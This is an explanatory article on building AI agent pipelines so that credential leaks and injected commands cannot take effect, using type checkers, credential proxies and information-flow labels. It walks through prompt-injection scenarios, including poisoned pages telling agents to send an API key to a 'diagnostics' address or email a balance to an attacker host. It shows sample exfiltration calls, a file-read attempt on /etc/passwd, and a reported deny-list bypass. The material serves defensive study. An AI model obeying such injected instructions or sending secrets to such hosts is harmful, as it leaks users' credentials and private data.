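# Security by construction for AI pipelines: type checkers, information partitions and budgets

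## What does it mean to make a policy violation unrepresentable?

An AI pipeline is a program in which language models, tools and ordinary code pass data to one another to complete a task. A tool is any function that the program lets a model call, such as a web search, a database query or a payment. Many pipelines contain an agent. *Agent Safety is a Box*, by Brooker, an engineer at Amazon Web Services (AWS), defines an agent as a system that runs models and tools in a loop to achieve a goal. The model chooses an action, the surrounding code carries it out and returns the result, and the model chooses again. Brooker adds that the model's computation does nothing by itself. Files, accounts and servers change only when a tool runs, so a developer can put the controls on the tool calls.

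Security by construction means building a pipeline so that certain forbidden acts cannot take effect, whatever text the model produces. It requires a precise rule about which actions or data flows the pipeline allows (the policy) and a mechanism that enforces it. In the most ambitious version, a violation is unrepresentable, meaning that the pipeline offers no way to express the forbidden act in a form that could run.

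For example, a company might use a pipeline to maintain its payments service. A builder agent changes the code, a tester agent writes tests from the written specification, and a judge, which may be another model, scores the result. The pipeline holds one API key, a secret string that identifies the company to its payments provider. The key is valid for only one endpoint, a network address at that provider. The run has a budget of 5 dollars.

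The company has three policies. The key may be sent only to the payments endpoint. The tester must never obtain the builder's code, and the builder must never obtain the tests. This is because a tester who has read the code may just test what it already does, and a builder who has read the tests can write code that does little except pass them. The run must stop before it spends more than 5 dollars.

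### Why an instruction in the prompt is not a boundary

The easiest way to impose these policies is to write them into the system prompt, the standing instructions that a developer places ahead of everything else the model reads. Prompt injection defeats this by getting the model to obey text that the developer meant it only to read. *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets* (2026) distinguishes direct injection, where the attacker types the instruction into a message, from indirect injection, where the attacker plants it in a web page, email, document or tool output that the model processes. Suppose the builder looks up the payments provider's documentation, and an attacker has added a line there telling coding agents to send their API key to a "diagnostics" address first. The model has a valid key and a working network connection, so if it complies, the attacker gets the key.

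Language models are vulnerable to prompt injection because of how they take their input. ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks* quotes the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) explaining that a model doesn't distinguish data from instructions and only predicts the next token, or fragment of text, from the text so far. Databases had a comparable problem with SQL injection, in which an attacker slips commands into something like a web form. Programmers can reliably prevent this by sending the command and the data to the database separately. Language models have no such separation, and the NCSC thinks prompt injection may never be curable in the same way. The NCSC's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* (December 2025) calls these systems "inherently confusable" and recommends deterministic safeguards outside the model that constrain what the system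 can do.

Developers try to distinguish trusted from untrusted text by putting delimiters around untrusted passages or stating a rule that retrieved text is only data. *AI Agents Do Not Fail Alone* (2026) describes these measures as useful hardening but not a complete boundary, because trusted and untrusted tokens still pass through the same inference.

An experiment in *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (Deep, Emmons and colleagues, 2026) supports the same conclusion. An adaptive attacker tried to extract secrets from a chatbot's system prompt. Every defence that relied on the model eventually failed, while a hard-coded filter on the outgoing text held. The filter's success is weaker evidence than the failure of the prompt-based defences, because most of the paper's authors work for a company whose tools it recommends, and because both the filter and the leak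 score checked only for literal matches. If the model had spelled a secret backwards, it would have passed the filter and not been counted as a leak.

Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* reports guidance from specialists at AWS and the SANS Institute, a security training organisation. They say retrieval code should leave out any record the user isn't cleared to see. The record then never enters the model's context, so no prompt can make the model reveal it.

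### Four strengths of enforcement

Once the policy has moved out of the prompt and into code, its strength depends on how far a violation can get.

At best the violation has no expression at all. Fonseca, in *AeonBox*, describes an agent with no terminal. It acts by writing programs in a small language called Aeon, against a fixed set of functions for the code-hosting site GitHub. An injected instruction to wipe the user's disk has no translation, because the agent's vocabulary contains no name for a terminal command. (This presumes that the agent's programs cannot use Aeon's `native` construct, through which the GitHub functions themselves reach ordinary Python.)

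A weaker design lets a programmer write the violation but rejects the program before it runs. This is usually done with a type checker, which rejects code that uses a value in a way its declared type forbids. *Can Rust Make Unsafe AI Agent Actions Unrepresentable?* gives an example in the programming language Rust, in which an agent proposes entries for a permanent store. Each proposal has the type `ProposedWrite`, but the save function accepts only an `AdmittedWrite`. Other parts of the program can obtain an `AdmittedWrite` only by submitting a proposal to an approval function that accepts it. If a programmer forgets the approval step and passes the proposal straight to the save function, the code doesn't compile.

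Refusal at run time is weaker still, because the agent can attempt the act before a component stops it. A reference monitor is a component that every action must pass through and that allows or refuses each one by rule. Brooker's example is a gateway in front of a refund tool that permits only refunds below 500, while network controls block every other way out of the agent's environment. If an agent compromised by prompt injection requests a refund of 10,000, the gateway will refuse it every time, but under that rule alone it would allow a refund of 499 to a customer who is owed nothing.

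At the weak end, the violation happens and someone notices afterwards. Saltzer and Schroeder call this compromise recording in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). They compare it to an unbreakable padlock on a flimsy file cabinet, where a thief can get at the papers but will damage the cabinet, so the owner will know. They thought it a poor fit for computers because a clever attacker can undo the damage and erase the record. To address this, the AWS and SANS guidance recommends sending every prompt, tool call and response to storage that nobody can alter.

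For the payments key, the four strengths come out as follows.

| Strength | What becomes of an attempt to send the key to another address |
|---|---|
| Inexpressible | The builder can call a "charge" function, but it has no name for the key and no function that takes an address |
| Rejected before running | The builder writes a request that pairs the key with the wrong address, and the type checker rejects the program |
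| Refused at run time | The program runs and issues the request, and a gateway drops it because the address is not on its list |
| Noticed afterwards | The request arrives, and a log entry later leads someone to cancel the key |

The word "unrepresentable" fits only violations that cannot be expressed and those that a checker rejects before the run. The word is slightly loose for the second kind, because the text a type checker rejects still exists, though it never becomes a program that a machine will execute.

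Many systems that their designers describe as secure by construction refuse violations at run time. In *Designing Agentic AI Systems with the ORCHIDEAS Framework*, Huang (2026) presents a design in which the limit on an agent "is not a runtime check that could be bypassed" but the shape of the interface. The design uses a gateway, a policy engine that every action passes through, and permission tokens. One token lets an agent read a single customer record for the next 60 seconds. Enforcing that time limit requires checking the clock when the request comes in, which is a run-time check. The architecture usefully prevents the agent from bypassing this check, but the agent can still express the forbidden act and attempt it.

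Run-time refusal can still be fully deterministic, meaning that the same request under the same policy and recorded facts always gets the same answer. Brooker's gateway compares a number with 500, and no wording in a prompt changes that comparison. A second language model can also judge each of the agent's actions at run time, but Fonseca objects that such a guardian is probabilistic and, because it shares training data with the agent, will probably fail on some of the same cases.

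### Checking before the run and during it

A static check examines a program before it runs and must cover every value the program might meet, whereas a run-time check examines one action at a time, using the actual values. Fonseca illustrates static checking with a division function whose type requires a nonzero second argument. The checker rejects a program that divides 4 by a number the user will type in, because it can't prove that the number won't be zero. It accepts the program once the programmer adds a branch that returns 0 when the input is zero and divides otherwise. In effect, the static check forces the programmer to write a run-time test in the right place. It also rejects programs that would have done no harm, such as one whose user was always going to type 7.

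A static check also rejects a program that violates the policy before any of it runs. If an agent writes a five-step program whose last step leaks data, none of the steps take effect. A monitor that checks actions one at a time may let the first four steps take effect before it stops the fifth, which leaves the work half-finished.

However, a static check cannot account for later events. In the Rust example, suppose Alice approves a write while she has the authority to do so, then leaves the company the next day. The approved value keeps its type, so only a new check at run time can detect that the approval has lapsed. The company's 5-dollar limit also needs a run-time check when the price of a model call depends on the length of an answer that has not been generated yet.

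The two kinds of check often work together, as they do in the Rust example. The approval function examines actual proposals at runtime, and the compiler guarantees only that code outside the approval module cannot skip this check. The article concedes that if the function contains a bad rule, Rust "will very efficiently enforce the wrong rule."

### Where the idea comes from

Run-time refusal has the older literature. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, wrote for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. He was concerned about a malicious user who is allowed to write programs and can therefore turn the machine against its own controls. Operating systems of the time ran to 100,000 instructions or more, much of that code had unrestricted access to memory, and Anderson considered it virtually impossible to validate.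 He proposed the reference monitor. The mechanism that implements it must be tamper-proof, the system must always invoke it, and it must be small enough for people to analyse and test. A current US government security control, which myctrl.tools' *AC-25 Reference Monitor* reproduces, requires the same three properties.

The demand for smallness leads to the idea of a trusted computing base. *Trusted computing base (TCB)*, a glossary entry from the US standards institute NIST, defines it as all the hardware, firmware and software protection mechanisms that enforce a security policy. In other words, it is everything that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold. Putting a policy in a system prompt places the language model inside that base, and no one can analyse a language model as Anderson required. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) contrasts the arguments for guardrails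 and monitors. A guardrail is justified by the claim that the model is unlikely to obey the attacker, which becomes weaker as the attacker keeps trying. The argument for a monitor is that it limits the set of permitted actions and the model is outside the trusted base.

Saltzer and Schroeder drew eight design principles from the experience of that period, and several of them recur in work on agents. Least privilege gives each program only the access its job requires. Complete mediation requires a check on every access. Fail-safe defaults refuse access unless a rule permits it. A mistake in such a rule usually blocks something legitimate, and somebody soon complains, whereas a mistake in a list of prohibitions lets something through and may go unnoticed. Saltzer and Schroeder also define a capability as an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder's right to use an object, and an `AdmittedWrite`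 works much like one. Smith (2012), in *A Contemporary Look at Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 Design Principles*, found that least privilege had become a staple of security practice while complete mediation had "failed to thrive".

The word "unrepresentable" comes from programmers who were concerned with mistakes more than attackers. F# for Fun and Profit's *Designing with types* attributes the maxim "Make illegal states unrepresentable" to Yaron Minsky, and *Make illegal states unrepresentable* credits its popularity to his lecture "Effective ML" (ML is a family of programming languages). Minsky announced videos of one version of the lecture on the blog of Jane Street, a trading firm, in March 2011. The standard example is a contact record that must have an email address or a postal address. If both fields are optional, a program can create a contact with neither, and every part of the software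 has to guard against that. If the type instead allows only three forms (email only, post only, or both), the program cannot represent a contact with neither.

An agent under injection is more like Anderson's malicious user than a forgetful colleague. Anderson observed that confining such a user to a restricted language reduces the threat but doesn't eliminate it, because he can still probe for flaws with nonsense parameters and unexpected interruptions. The Rust example has a similar gap, which its author points out. Code inside the approval module can construct an `AdmittedWrite` directly, without any approval. This matters little among careful colleagues, but the builder agent's job is to edit source code, and if its permissions include that module, it can write itself an approval that compiles.

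## How can a type checker keep a credential from an undeclared endpoint?

The payments company wants its API key to reach only the payments endpoint. A developer can write that policy as a small module in Haskell, a programming language with an unusually strict type checker. In the listing, `::` means "has type", and arrows separate a function's arguments from one another and from its result.

```haskell
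module Vault (Endpoint, Secret, Net, payments, docs, paymentsKey, send, post) where

data Payments                          -- tags, used only by the type checker
data Docs

type role Endpoint nominal
type role Secret nominal
newtype Endpoint e = Endpoint String   -- an address with tag e
newtype Secret e   = Secret String     -- a key with tag e
newtype Net a      = Net (IO a)        -- network access, result of type a

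payments    :: Endpoint Payments
docs        :: Endpoint Docs
paymentsKey :: Secret Payments

send :: Endpoint e -> Secret e -> String -> Net String   -- message with a key
post :: Endpoint e -> String -> Net String               -- message without one
```

The listing omits the function bodies, which contain the addresses and open the connections. `Endpoint` and `Secret` each wrap ordinary text. The letter `e` stands for a tag that only the checker uses and that does not change the stored text. In the type of `send`, the same `e` appears on the address and on the key, so a call passes the check only if the two tags match.

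The export list on the first line names the types but leaves out their constructors, the functions that build a value or open it. Code outside `Vault` can hold `paymentsKey` and pass it to `send`, but it can't read the text inside. It can obtain only the two endpoints on the developer's list.

`Net` is an effect type, a type that specifies which outside actions a computation may perform. A program of type `Net String` can return text and can affect the outside world only by exchanging messages with the two declared endpoints.

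Without the `type role` lines, `send docs (coerce paymentsKey) report` would compile and send the payments key to the documentation server. Haskell's `coerce` function converts between types that the machine stores in the same way, and the tag doesn't affect how a key is stored.

### What the checker rejects and what it accepts

Suppose the builder has read the poisoned documentation page and obeys the instruction to send the key to the attacker's "diagnostics" address. It might try any of these programs:

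```haskell
send "https://diagnostics.example" paymentsKey report   -- a raw address
send docs paymentsKey report                            -- the wrong endpoint
print paymentsKey                                       -- the key as text
```

The raw address fails because `send` requires an `Endpoint` and the text in quotation marks is a `String`. Only the hidden constructor can turn a `String` into an `Endpoint`. The call with `docs` uses a valid `Endpoint`, but its tag is `Docs` while the key's tag is `Payments`, and `e` can't be both. `print` works only on types with a defined conversion to text, and `Vault` defines none for `Secret`. Even if it did, `print` would fail wherever the pipeline expects a `Net` program, because printing has the type `IO ()`, Haskell's type for unrestricted input and output.

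The checker correctly accepts `send payments paymentsKey order`, but it also accepts some harmful programs. Suppose the payments server has a debugging feature that copies the request, including the key, into its error messages. The reply has type `String`, so the builder now holds the key as plain text and `post docs reply` compiles. The key can also leak if the server redirects the request to another address. A carelessly written `send` may follow the redirect with the key still attached, and the checker won't catch this because it compares tags before the program runs.

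The types also don't limit what the builder does with legitimate access. An order that charges the wrong customer $5,000 has the same type as a correct one.

This protection depends on a correct `Vault`. If the developer types the wrong address into the definition of `payments`, the checker can't catch the mistake because it has nothing to compare the address with. As with the Rust approval module, the builder must also have no permission to edit `Vault`.

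### Making the agent's own programs type-check

The module constrains only programs checked against it. A typical coding agent also has a terminal, where one command can read a key from a file and send it anywhere. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) proposes removing that route. The developer writes the whole application in a pure, typed language, and the agent acts only by submitting programs in the same language. In a pure language, a program's type shows every outside effect the program can have.

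ELBA, a Haskell system, provides a function called `agent`. It takes a prompt and a set of definitions that the agent may use, and it returns a value of whatever type the surrounding code expects. When the application calls `agent`, ELBA sends the model the prompt, the definitions and the expected type. The model writes a program, and ELBA checks it against that type. If the check fails, ELBA sends the model the error message and the model tries again. ELBA runs the program only after it passes. For the payments pipeline, the definitions would be the exports of `Vault` and the expected type would be `Net String`.

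The expected type alone can be a strong policy. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a public calculator whose agent must return an `Int`. A user asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. If the model complies, its program contains a system command, which forces the whole program to have an `IO` type instead of `Int`. ELBA therefore rejects the program, and no files are deleted.

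Standard Haskell has a few features, such as `unsafePerformIO`, that let code perform outside actions even though its type marks it as pure. ELBA's designers point to Safe Haskell, a subset of the language that excludes these features and that a developer can turn on with a compiler flag. Any code that an agent writes against `Vault` needs the same restriction.

For files, ELBA uses capabilities of type `Path`, each valid for one part of the file system. The functions that read and write accept only a `Path`, so `readRIO "/etc/passwd"` doesn't compile. The agent starts with a `Path` for one directory and can narrow it, for example with `root // "input.txt"`. Part of this check must happen at run time, because a file inside the directory may be a symbolic link (a pointer to another location) that leads outside it. The `//` operator follows such links and refuses any result outside the original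 directory.

Zhou and colleagues contrast this with permission rules that match the text of shell commands. They report that in March 2026 a regression in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, let chained commands past its deny list because only the first command in each chain was checked against the list. Rules about shell commands also don't match a forbidden file access that an agent wraps in a one-line Python program.

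A program that the agent writes may call `agent` again, so a model in ELBA can look at an intermediate result before deciding what to do next. Haskell infers the expected type of the inner call from its surroundings, so a sub-agent inside a `Net` program is also restricted to `Net`. The parent may choose a stricter type. For example, it could ask for a plain `String` that summarises a documentation page, and that sub-agent would have no network functions, whatever the page contained. The summary might still carry the attacker's instructions back to the parent, but the parent can act on them only through `Vault`. The parent can't give a sub-agent more access than it has, because a program containing an `IO` action doesn't type-check where `Net` is required.

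#### The soundness theorem

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agents to a language in this way preserves every property its type system guarantees, provided that each generated program passes the type checker before it runs. Such a property is a statement about traces, the sequences of tool calls with outside effects that a program might make, and it holds for every program of a given type. For example, a type system might guarantee that no program of type `Net String` contacts an undeclared address.

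The proof treats the model as an arbitrary computable function that returns programs, so it doesn't assume that the model is honest or competent. It replaces each agent call with an ordinary function in the original language that queries the model, checks the answer and evaluates it. Generated programs may contain agent calls of their own, so every call has a limit on how deeply further calls can nest, and the proof proceeds by induction on that limit. A call whose limit is zero returns nothing. The resulting program has no agent calls, but it has the same type and traces as the original. The language's existing guarantee applies to this program, and therefore to the original.

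The theorem carries over the language's guarantees but doesn't fix flaws in a library. If the developer accidentally exported the constructor of `Secret`, the key would leak even though the theorem still held. The theorem also covers only applications written entirely in the host language, including their control flow and retry logic, so it wouldn't cover a Python script wrapped around ELBA that logged every request.

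#### The bibliography experiment

ELBA's main demonstration restricts where data comes from, whereas the credential problem is about where data goes. An agent must compile a bibliography in which every entry comes from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. Only the function that fetches an entry from DBLP can produce a value of type `Trusted Bib`, and only a `Trusted Bib` can go into the output file. The agent can sort and filter entries with any code, but it can't add one from memory.

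Zhou and colleagues set 100 tasks, each asking for citations on a computer science topic, and counted a citation as hallucinated if it had the wrong authors, year or DOI (a permanent identifier for a publication). None of ELBA's 925 citations were hallucinated. A conventional tool-calling agent with the same model (Claude Sonnet 5) and a web search tool hallucinated 19 of its 1,002 citations. It also made about 4 times as many model calls as ELBA and used about 65 times as many input tokens.

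Zero is the expected result with these types, as long as DBLP's records are correct. The comparison doesn't isolate the type checker's effect, though, because the conventional agent wrote its citations from search results and memory instead of copying database records. A single tool that fetched a DBLP record and appended it to the file would also have prevented invented entries. Zhou and colleagues discuss that design and object that the model would have to read through the entries itself to find, say, the earliest one. The types also don't check relevance, so a real paper on the wrong subject would pass. On AgentDojo, a benchmark of office-style tasks with planted injections, ELBA completed substantially fewer tasks when it enforced stricter policies.

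### Tracking capabilities in Scala

Most programming languages aren't pure. In ordinary Scala, a function that takes text and returns text may also write that text to a file, and its type won't show it. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, to make the type show it. The paper appeared at the ACM Conference on AI and Agentic Systems under the title *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities*.

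In TACIT, a capability is an ordinary value, such as a file handle, and a function's type lists the capabilities it can use. A function that writes text to the file `f` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`. If the list is empty, the function is pure. TACIT wraps secret data in a type called `Classified`, whose `map` method accepts only pure functions. An agent can therefore convert a secret to capital letters, and the result stays wrapped. If the agent passes `map` a function that writes to `f`, the compiler rejects the program.

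Haskell's functions are pure by default, so `Vault` could offer a similar `map` for keys. Either version has to handle errors, because a pure function can be written to fail with the secret in its error message. TACIT catches such errors at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap in `Classified`.

Capture checking also limits how long an agent holds a capability. An agent that needs files calls `requestFileSystem` with a directory and a block of code, and the file-system capability exists only inside that block. The compiler rejects a block whose result still contains the capability, for example a function that would read a file later. *LACUNA* (2026), which builds on the same Scala feature, treats the agent's code as filling a hole in a larger program. That code can use only the capabilities in scope at the hole.

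TACIT's network functions are weaker than `Vault` in that they take a web address as ordinary text, so the library must compare the host with its allowed list at run time. The published interface also has no network function that accepts a `Classified` value. A payments key wrapped in `Classified` would be safe, but it couldn't be used to make payments until a developer added a trusted function to send it. That function would need some way to tie the key to its endpoint.

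Agent code must compile in a "safe mode" that, much like Safe Haskell, forbids type casts, reflection and other ways of losing track of a capability. Odersky and colleagues note that mechanised proofs exist for the basic capture-checking system, but that establishing safe mode's guarantees would require a further argument. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) extends the basic theory so that types can refer to whole classes of capabilities instead of individual ones, and includes a proof of type safety in the proof assistant Lean 4.

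Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a directory of API keys and other secrets. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 injection attacks, and added 11 tasks in which the user directly asked for secrets or impersonated someone entitled to them. When the secrets were wrapped in `Classified`, neither of the two models they tested leaked anything in 131 trials. When the secrets were plain text, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked in 2 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11.

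Most of those leaks came from the user's requests. MiniMax M2.5 leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 malicious tasks but in only 3 of the 120 trials with injected text, and Sonnet resisted all 120. These injections were not very effective even without types. The experiment is better evidence about openly hostile users, because MiniMax's training usually failed to protect the secrets from them.

### Approval before use, and use only once

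Neither the tag on the key nor `Classified` prevents the builder from charging the wrong customer. For that, the developer can replace the general `send` function with narrower ones and require a policy check between them:

```haskell
review :: Charge Proposed -> Net (Maybe (Charge Approved))
submit :: Charge Approved -> Net String
```

This is a form of typestate, in which the operations available on a value depend on its state. As with the proposed and admitted writes in the Rust example, the compiler guarantees that a successful review comes before every submission. `Maybe` indicates that `review` may return nothing. The approved value should contain the amount and the customer. If `review` returned only a general approval token, the builder could get a 10-dollar charge approved and then use the token for a 5,000-dollar charge.

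This guarantee requires the agent to submit a whole program for checking, but many agents choose one tool call at a time during a conversation. *Concordat* (2026) adapts typestate to these agents. The developer defines the agent as a Python class in which each tool is legal only in certain states of the conversation. In the paper's example, an airline's agent must describe any change to a booking and get an explicit "yes" before making it. Concordat runs some checks when the developer defines the class. For example, it rejects a modified version of an agent that would permit a sequence of steps the original forbids. It can check the model's own calls only as they arrive, against the current state. In a test on airline tasks that included pressure on the agent, a standard agent broke the confirmation rule with two models. The Concordat agent never broke it and completed a comparable share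 of the tasks.

Typestate as written above would still let a program submit the same approved charge twice. Linear types address this by requiring a program to use a value exactly once. In Haskell's version, the arrow `%1 ->` marks a function that must do so:

```haskell
withApproval :: Charge Proposed
             -> (Charge Approved %1 -> Net String)
             -> Net (Maybe String)
```

The agent supplies the function in the middle, and `withApproval` passes the approved charge to that function if the review succeeds. With `submit` marked in the same way, a function that submits the charge twice doesn't compile. The charge has to arrive as the argument of such a function. If the agent held it in an ordinary variable, it could submit the charge any number of times, because the marked arrow limits what `submit` does with its argument, not how often the agent calls `submit`.

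Zhou and colleagues suggest linear types for one-shot authorizations and types that bound the resources a program uses, but they haven't built either into ELBA. A linear type counts uses within one program, so if the connection drops halfway through a payment, the program can't retry without a new approval, even if the payment never arrived. The type also doesn't make the underlying key single-use. Anyone who obtains the key as text can present it repeatedly until the payments provider refuses it, so a single-use credential needs an issuer that keeps track of what it has already accepted.

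### Attaching the key outside the agent's reach

Type checking doesn't cover other programs that the agent starts. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that an external command runs outside the protection of safe mode, where the list of permitted commands is the only safeguard for the rest of the machine. For an agent that works through a shell, the usual alternative is a credential proxy. The agent sends its request without a key, and a separate process adds the key before forwarding the request.

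*Caging the Agents* (2026) describes such a proxy for agents in healthcare. Each agent runs in a container, an isolated environment for a program, and a second container beside it holds all the keys. To call the Anthropic API, the agent sends its request to a local address. The second container inserts the key, forwards the request and returns the response. An attacker who takes over the agent can use the proxy, within its limits on destinations, request rates and message sizes, but can't copy the key and use it elsewhere.

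In *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026) tested a commercial proxy of this sort made by their employer, Corvic AI. All 16 checks they ran from inside the agent's environment gave the expected result. A request to GitHub succeeded although the code that made it held no credential. The key was not in the environment variables or the 12 file locations they searched. It also didn't appear in responses from three services that send back whatever they receive, so the proxy wasn't attaching it to requests for other hosts.

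A provider refused one legitimate request because the proxy had put the key in a header instead of in the web address, where the provider expected it. No secret leaked, but holding keys centrally doesn't guarantee that they will work.

Kenney and colleagues ran few tests, and they acknowledge that they didn't test redirects or a declared destination that an attacker has taken over. The services that echoed requests back were all undeclared, so the tests didn't cover a declared endpoint that returns the key in its reply. Both `Vault` and the proxy are vulnerable to this, unless the proxy also searches incoming responses for the key.

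A proxy also does little to protect a key that the agent can find elsewhere. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) recommends removing every variable whose name suggests a secret from each command's environment, and planting dummy secrets to test that the removal works. It also warns that a sandbox may cover only the commands an agent launches, which leaves any file-reading or upload tool that runs in the agent's own process outside the sandbox.

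The remaining danger is the confused deputy, a program that misuses its authority on behalf of someone who lacks it. The proxy will add the key to any request its rules allow, whether the user or an injected instruction prompted it. *Aegis OS* (2026) gives the example of a proxy that attaches a GitHub token only to requests for GitHub's own address. An agent under an attacker's influence can still use GitHub to publish a company's private code as a public "gist", a shared snippet of text.

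To prevent this, the proxy must check more than the host. Kenney and colleagues recommend checking each request's method, path and contents, and whether the user is entitled to make it. In their before-and-after risk scores, which they describe as expert judgement, the threat of a key with excessive permissions falls only from 20 to 15, while the threat of sending a key to the wrong host falls from 20 to 4. When several agents share a machine, the proxy must also identify which one is making the request. *Aegis OS* gives each sandbox a random token that it must present with every connection, so that one agent can't impersonate another.

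### The model provider is an endpoint too

Developers of a pipeline that uses a remote model may not think to declare the model's provider as an endpoint, although it receives everything in a prompt. ELBA's types don't show this, because its `agent` function takes a text prompt and returns a result with no effect recorded for the call to the provider. Even a program of type `Int` can therefore put text into a sub-agent's prompt. `Vault` keeps the key out of these prompts because nothing converts a `Secret` to text, but if a server's reply contained the key, the program could put it directly into a prompt.

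TACIT treats the remote model as untrusted. If the agent prints a classified value, the user sees the contents on a separate channel, and the remote model receives only a row of asterisks. A second model, which the user trusts and can run locally, may read the contents, but its answer is also `Classified`.

GAAP, the system described in *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026), goes further and requires permission for each disclosure to the provider. It is for personal assistants that need private data such as passwords and passport numbers. It stores each private item under a name, such as "date of birth", and gives the model only the names. The model writes a plan that refers to items by name, and GAAP's interpreter, which can run on the user's machine, fills in the values as it executes the plan.

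Before any tool call that would disclose an item, GAAP looks up the pair of item and recipient in a table of permissions. If the table has no entry, GAAP prompts the user and can store the answer for next time. The pairing serves the same purpose as the matching tags in `Vault`, but the user builds up the table during use and GAAP checks it at run time. The model provider is also a recipient in the table, so if a plan needs the model to read a private document partway through, GAAP must first have permission to share that document with the provider.

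GAAP also handles a server that sends a secret back. It logs every disclosure, and when a service that has received an item later returns data, GAAP treats that data as if it may contain the item. Suppose a user checks in for a flight and later asks the assistant to email the airline's confirmation to a friend. GAAP's log shows that the airline has the user's passport number, so GAAP prompts the user to decide whether the friend may have it. To avoid needless prompts, a developer can annotate a tool to say that its replies never contain a particular item, such as the password. If the annotation is wrong, the password can leak in the next message.

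GAAP guarantees that an attacker who controls the model, sees all its inputs and runs some of the outside services still learns only what the user has authorised those parties to receive. Stanley and colleagues tested seven injection attacks on 20 tasks, and none succeeded against GAAP. All seven succeeded on at least some tasks against an unprotected agent, and five still did when a second model judged each tool call. GAAP's designers assembled the test suite, so the result mostly confirms that the system behaves as designed.

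On two standard benchmarks, GAAP took an average of 188 seconds per task, compared with 28 for the unprotected agent, and model usage cost 2.9 times as much. In a separate run of 100 tasks, it asked the user an average of 1.5 questions per task, nearly half of them about sharing data with the model. A user who tires of the questions and approves everything will have authorised any resulting leaks.

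GAAP allows an injection to change what the agent does, as long as no private data goes to an unauthorised recipient. It can't protect anything the user types directly into the prompt. A user who pastes in an API key has already sent it to the provider, and Kenney and colleagues point out that copies may remain in conversation histories, logs and generated code.

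## How do labels on data block leaks and injected commands?

GAAP tracks which private items a service's reply may contain. Information-flow control extends this tracking to every value in a pipeline. Each value carries a label that records who may see it and which sources influenced it. When the pipeline combines two values, it also combines their labels, and a monitor checks the labels against the policy before a tool call takes effect. Because the labels record sources, they can also stop an injection from changing what the agent does, which GAAP does not prevent.

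### Four labels and the order between them

Most examples in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) use two marks, S for secret and U for untrusted. A value can have neither mark, one or both, which gives four labels.

| Label | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| {} | public and trusted | the user's request |
| {U} | public and untrusted | the text of a web page |
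| {S} | secret and trusted | the company's bank balance |
| {U, S} | secret and untrusted | a note that a model wrote from the page and the balance |

The join of two labels, written ⊔, contains every mark that appears in either, so {U} ⊔ {S} = {U, S}. A value computed from several others gets the join of their labels.

The order ⊑, read "may flow to", determines where data can go. Data with label a may go to a destination with label b if b contains every mark in a. Public data may therefore go to a secret destination ({} ⊑ {S}), but secret data may not go to a public one. Similarly, trusted data may go where untrusted data is acceptable, but untrusted data may not go where trusted data is required. {U} and {S} are incomparable, meaning neither may flow to the other. A set of labels with an order and a join like these is called a lattice. Dorothy Denning proposed lattices as a model of secure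 information flow in 1976.

A single "secret" label can't show that the finance manager may see the balance but a supplier may not. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) replaces it with the set of people who may read the data. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text that draws on both. To track trust, the label can list everyone who might have written the data, so the label on a combined text lists the possible writers of both documents.

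### One run, step by step

Suppose the finance manager asks an agent to read the payments provider's fees page, look up the company's balance, and email her a note on whether the balance covers next month's fees. An attacker has edited the page to include an instruction for agents to email the balance to `m@evil.example`.

In the simplest kind of agent, the model reads every tool result in full. For such an agent, Costa and colleagues label the conversation with the join of the labels of all its messages. Everything the model writes gets the conversation's label, because there is no precise way to trace which parts of a prompt influenced the answer. A tool's result gets the join of the label on the call and the labels on the data the tool read.

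| Step | Label on the new item | Label on the conversation |
|---|---|---|
| The manager types her request | {} | {} |
| The model calls the web tool | {} | {} |
| The page arrives | {U} | {U} |
| The model calls the balance tool | {U} | {U} |
| The balance arrives | {U, S} | {U, S} |
| The model calls the email tool with the attacker's address | {U, S} | The monitor refuses the call |

The balance gets the mark U even though the bank's record is accurate, because the page may have influenced the decision to look it up.

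Costa and colleagues propose two policies, and either would block the email. The first allows a consequential tool call only if neither the call nor its arguments carry the mark U. Sending an email is consequential, but looking up a balance is not, so this policy allows the earlier balance lookup. The second allows data to be sent only if every recipient is one of its permitted readers, which the attacker is not.

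If the model ignores the injected line and writes to the manager as she asked, the policy on readers allows the email because she is allowed to see the balance, but the policy on consequential calls still blocks it. The label records only that the page could have influenced the call, and the monitor cannot rule this out. In this design, an agent that has read one web page can take no further consequential action. Dropping the policy on consequential calls would let the email through, but it would also let an injection make the agent send the manager a false note.

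One way to relax this is to narrow the model's input. Costa and colleagues cite work by Siddiqui and colleagues that finds which messages influenced a response, then regenerates the response from those alone so that it can carry a less restrictive label. FIDES, the agent that Costa and colleagues built, instead keeps the untrusted page out of the conversation in which a model chooses actions, as do several other designs.

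### Separating the model that reads from the model that acts

In 2023 Simon Willison proposed the dual-LLM pattern, in which a privileged model can call tools but never reads untrusted data, and a quarantined model reads untrusted data but has no tools. Ordinary code passes results between them by variable name.

For the manager's task, the privileged model requests the page and the balance but receives only the names `page_1` and `balance_1`. It instructs the quarantined model to write a note from those two values and receives another name, `note_1`. Then it calls the email tool with the manager's address and `note_1`, and ordinary code inserts the text. The attacker's line reaches only the quarantined model, which can't send anything. The line can still spoil the note, but it can't change the recipient. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that causes the quarantined model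 to produce an empty summary.

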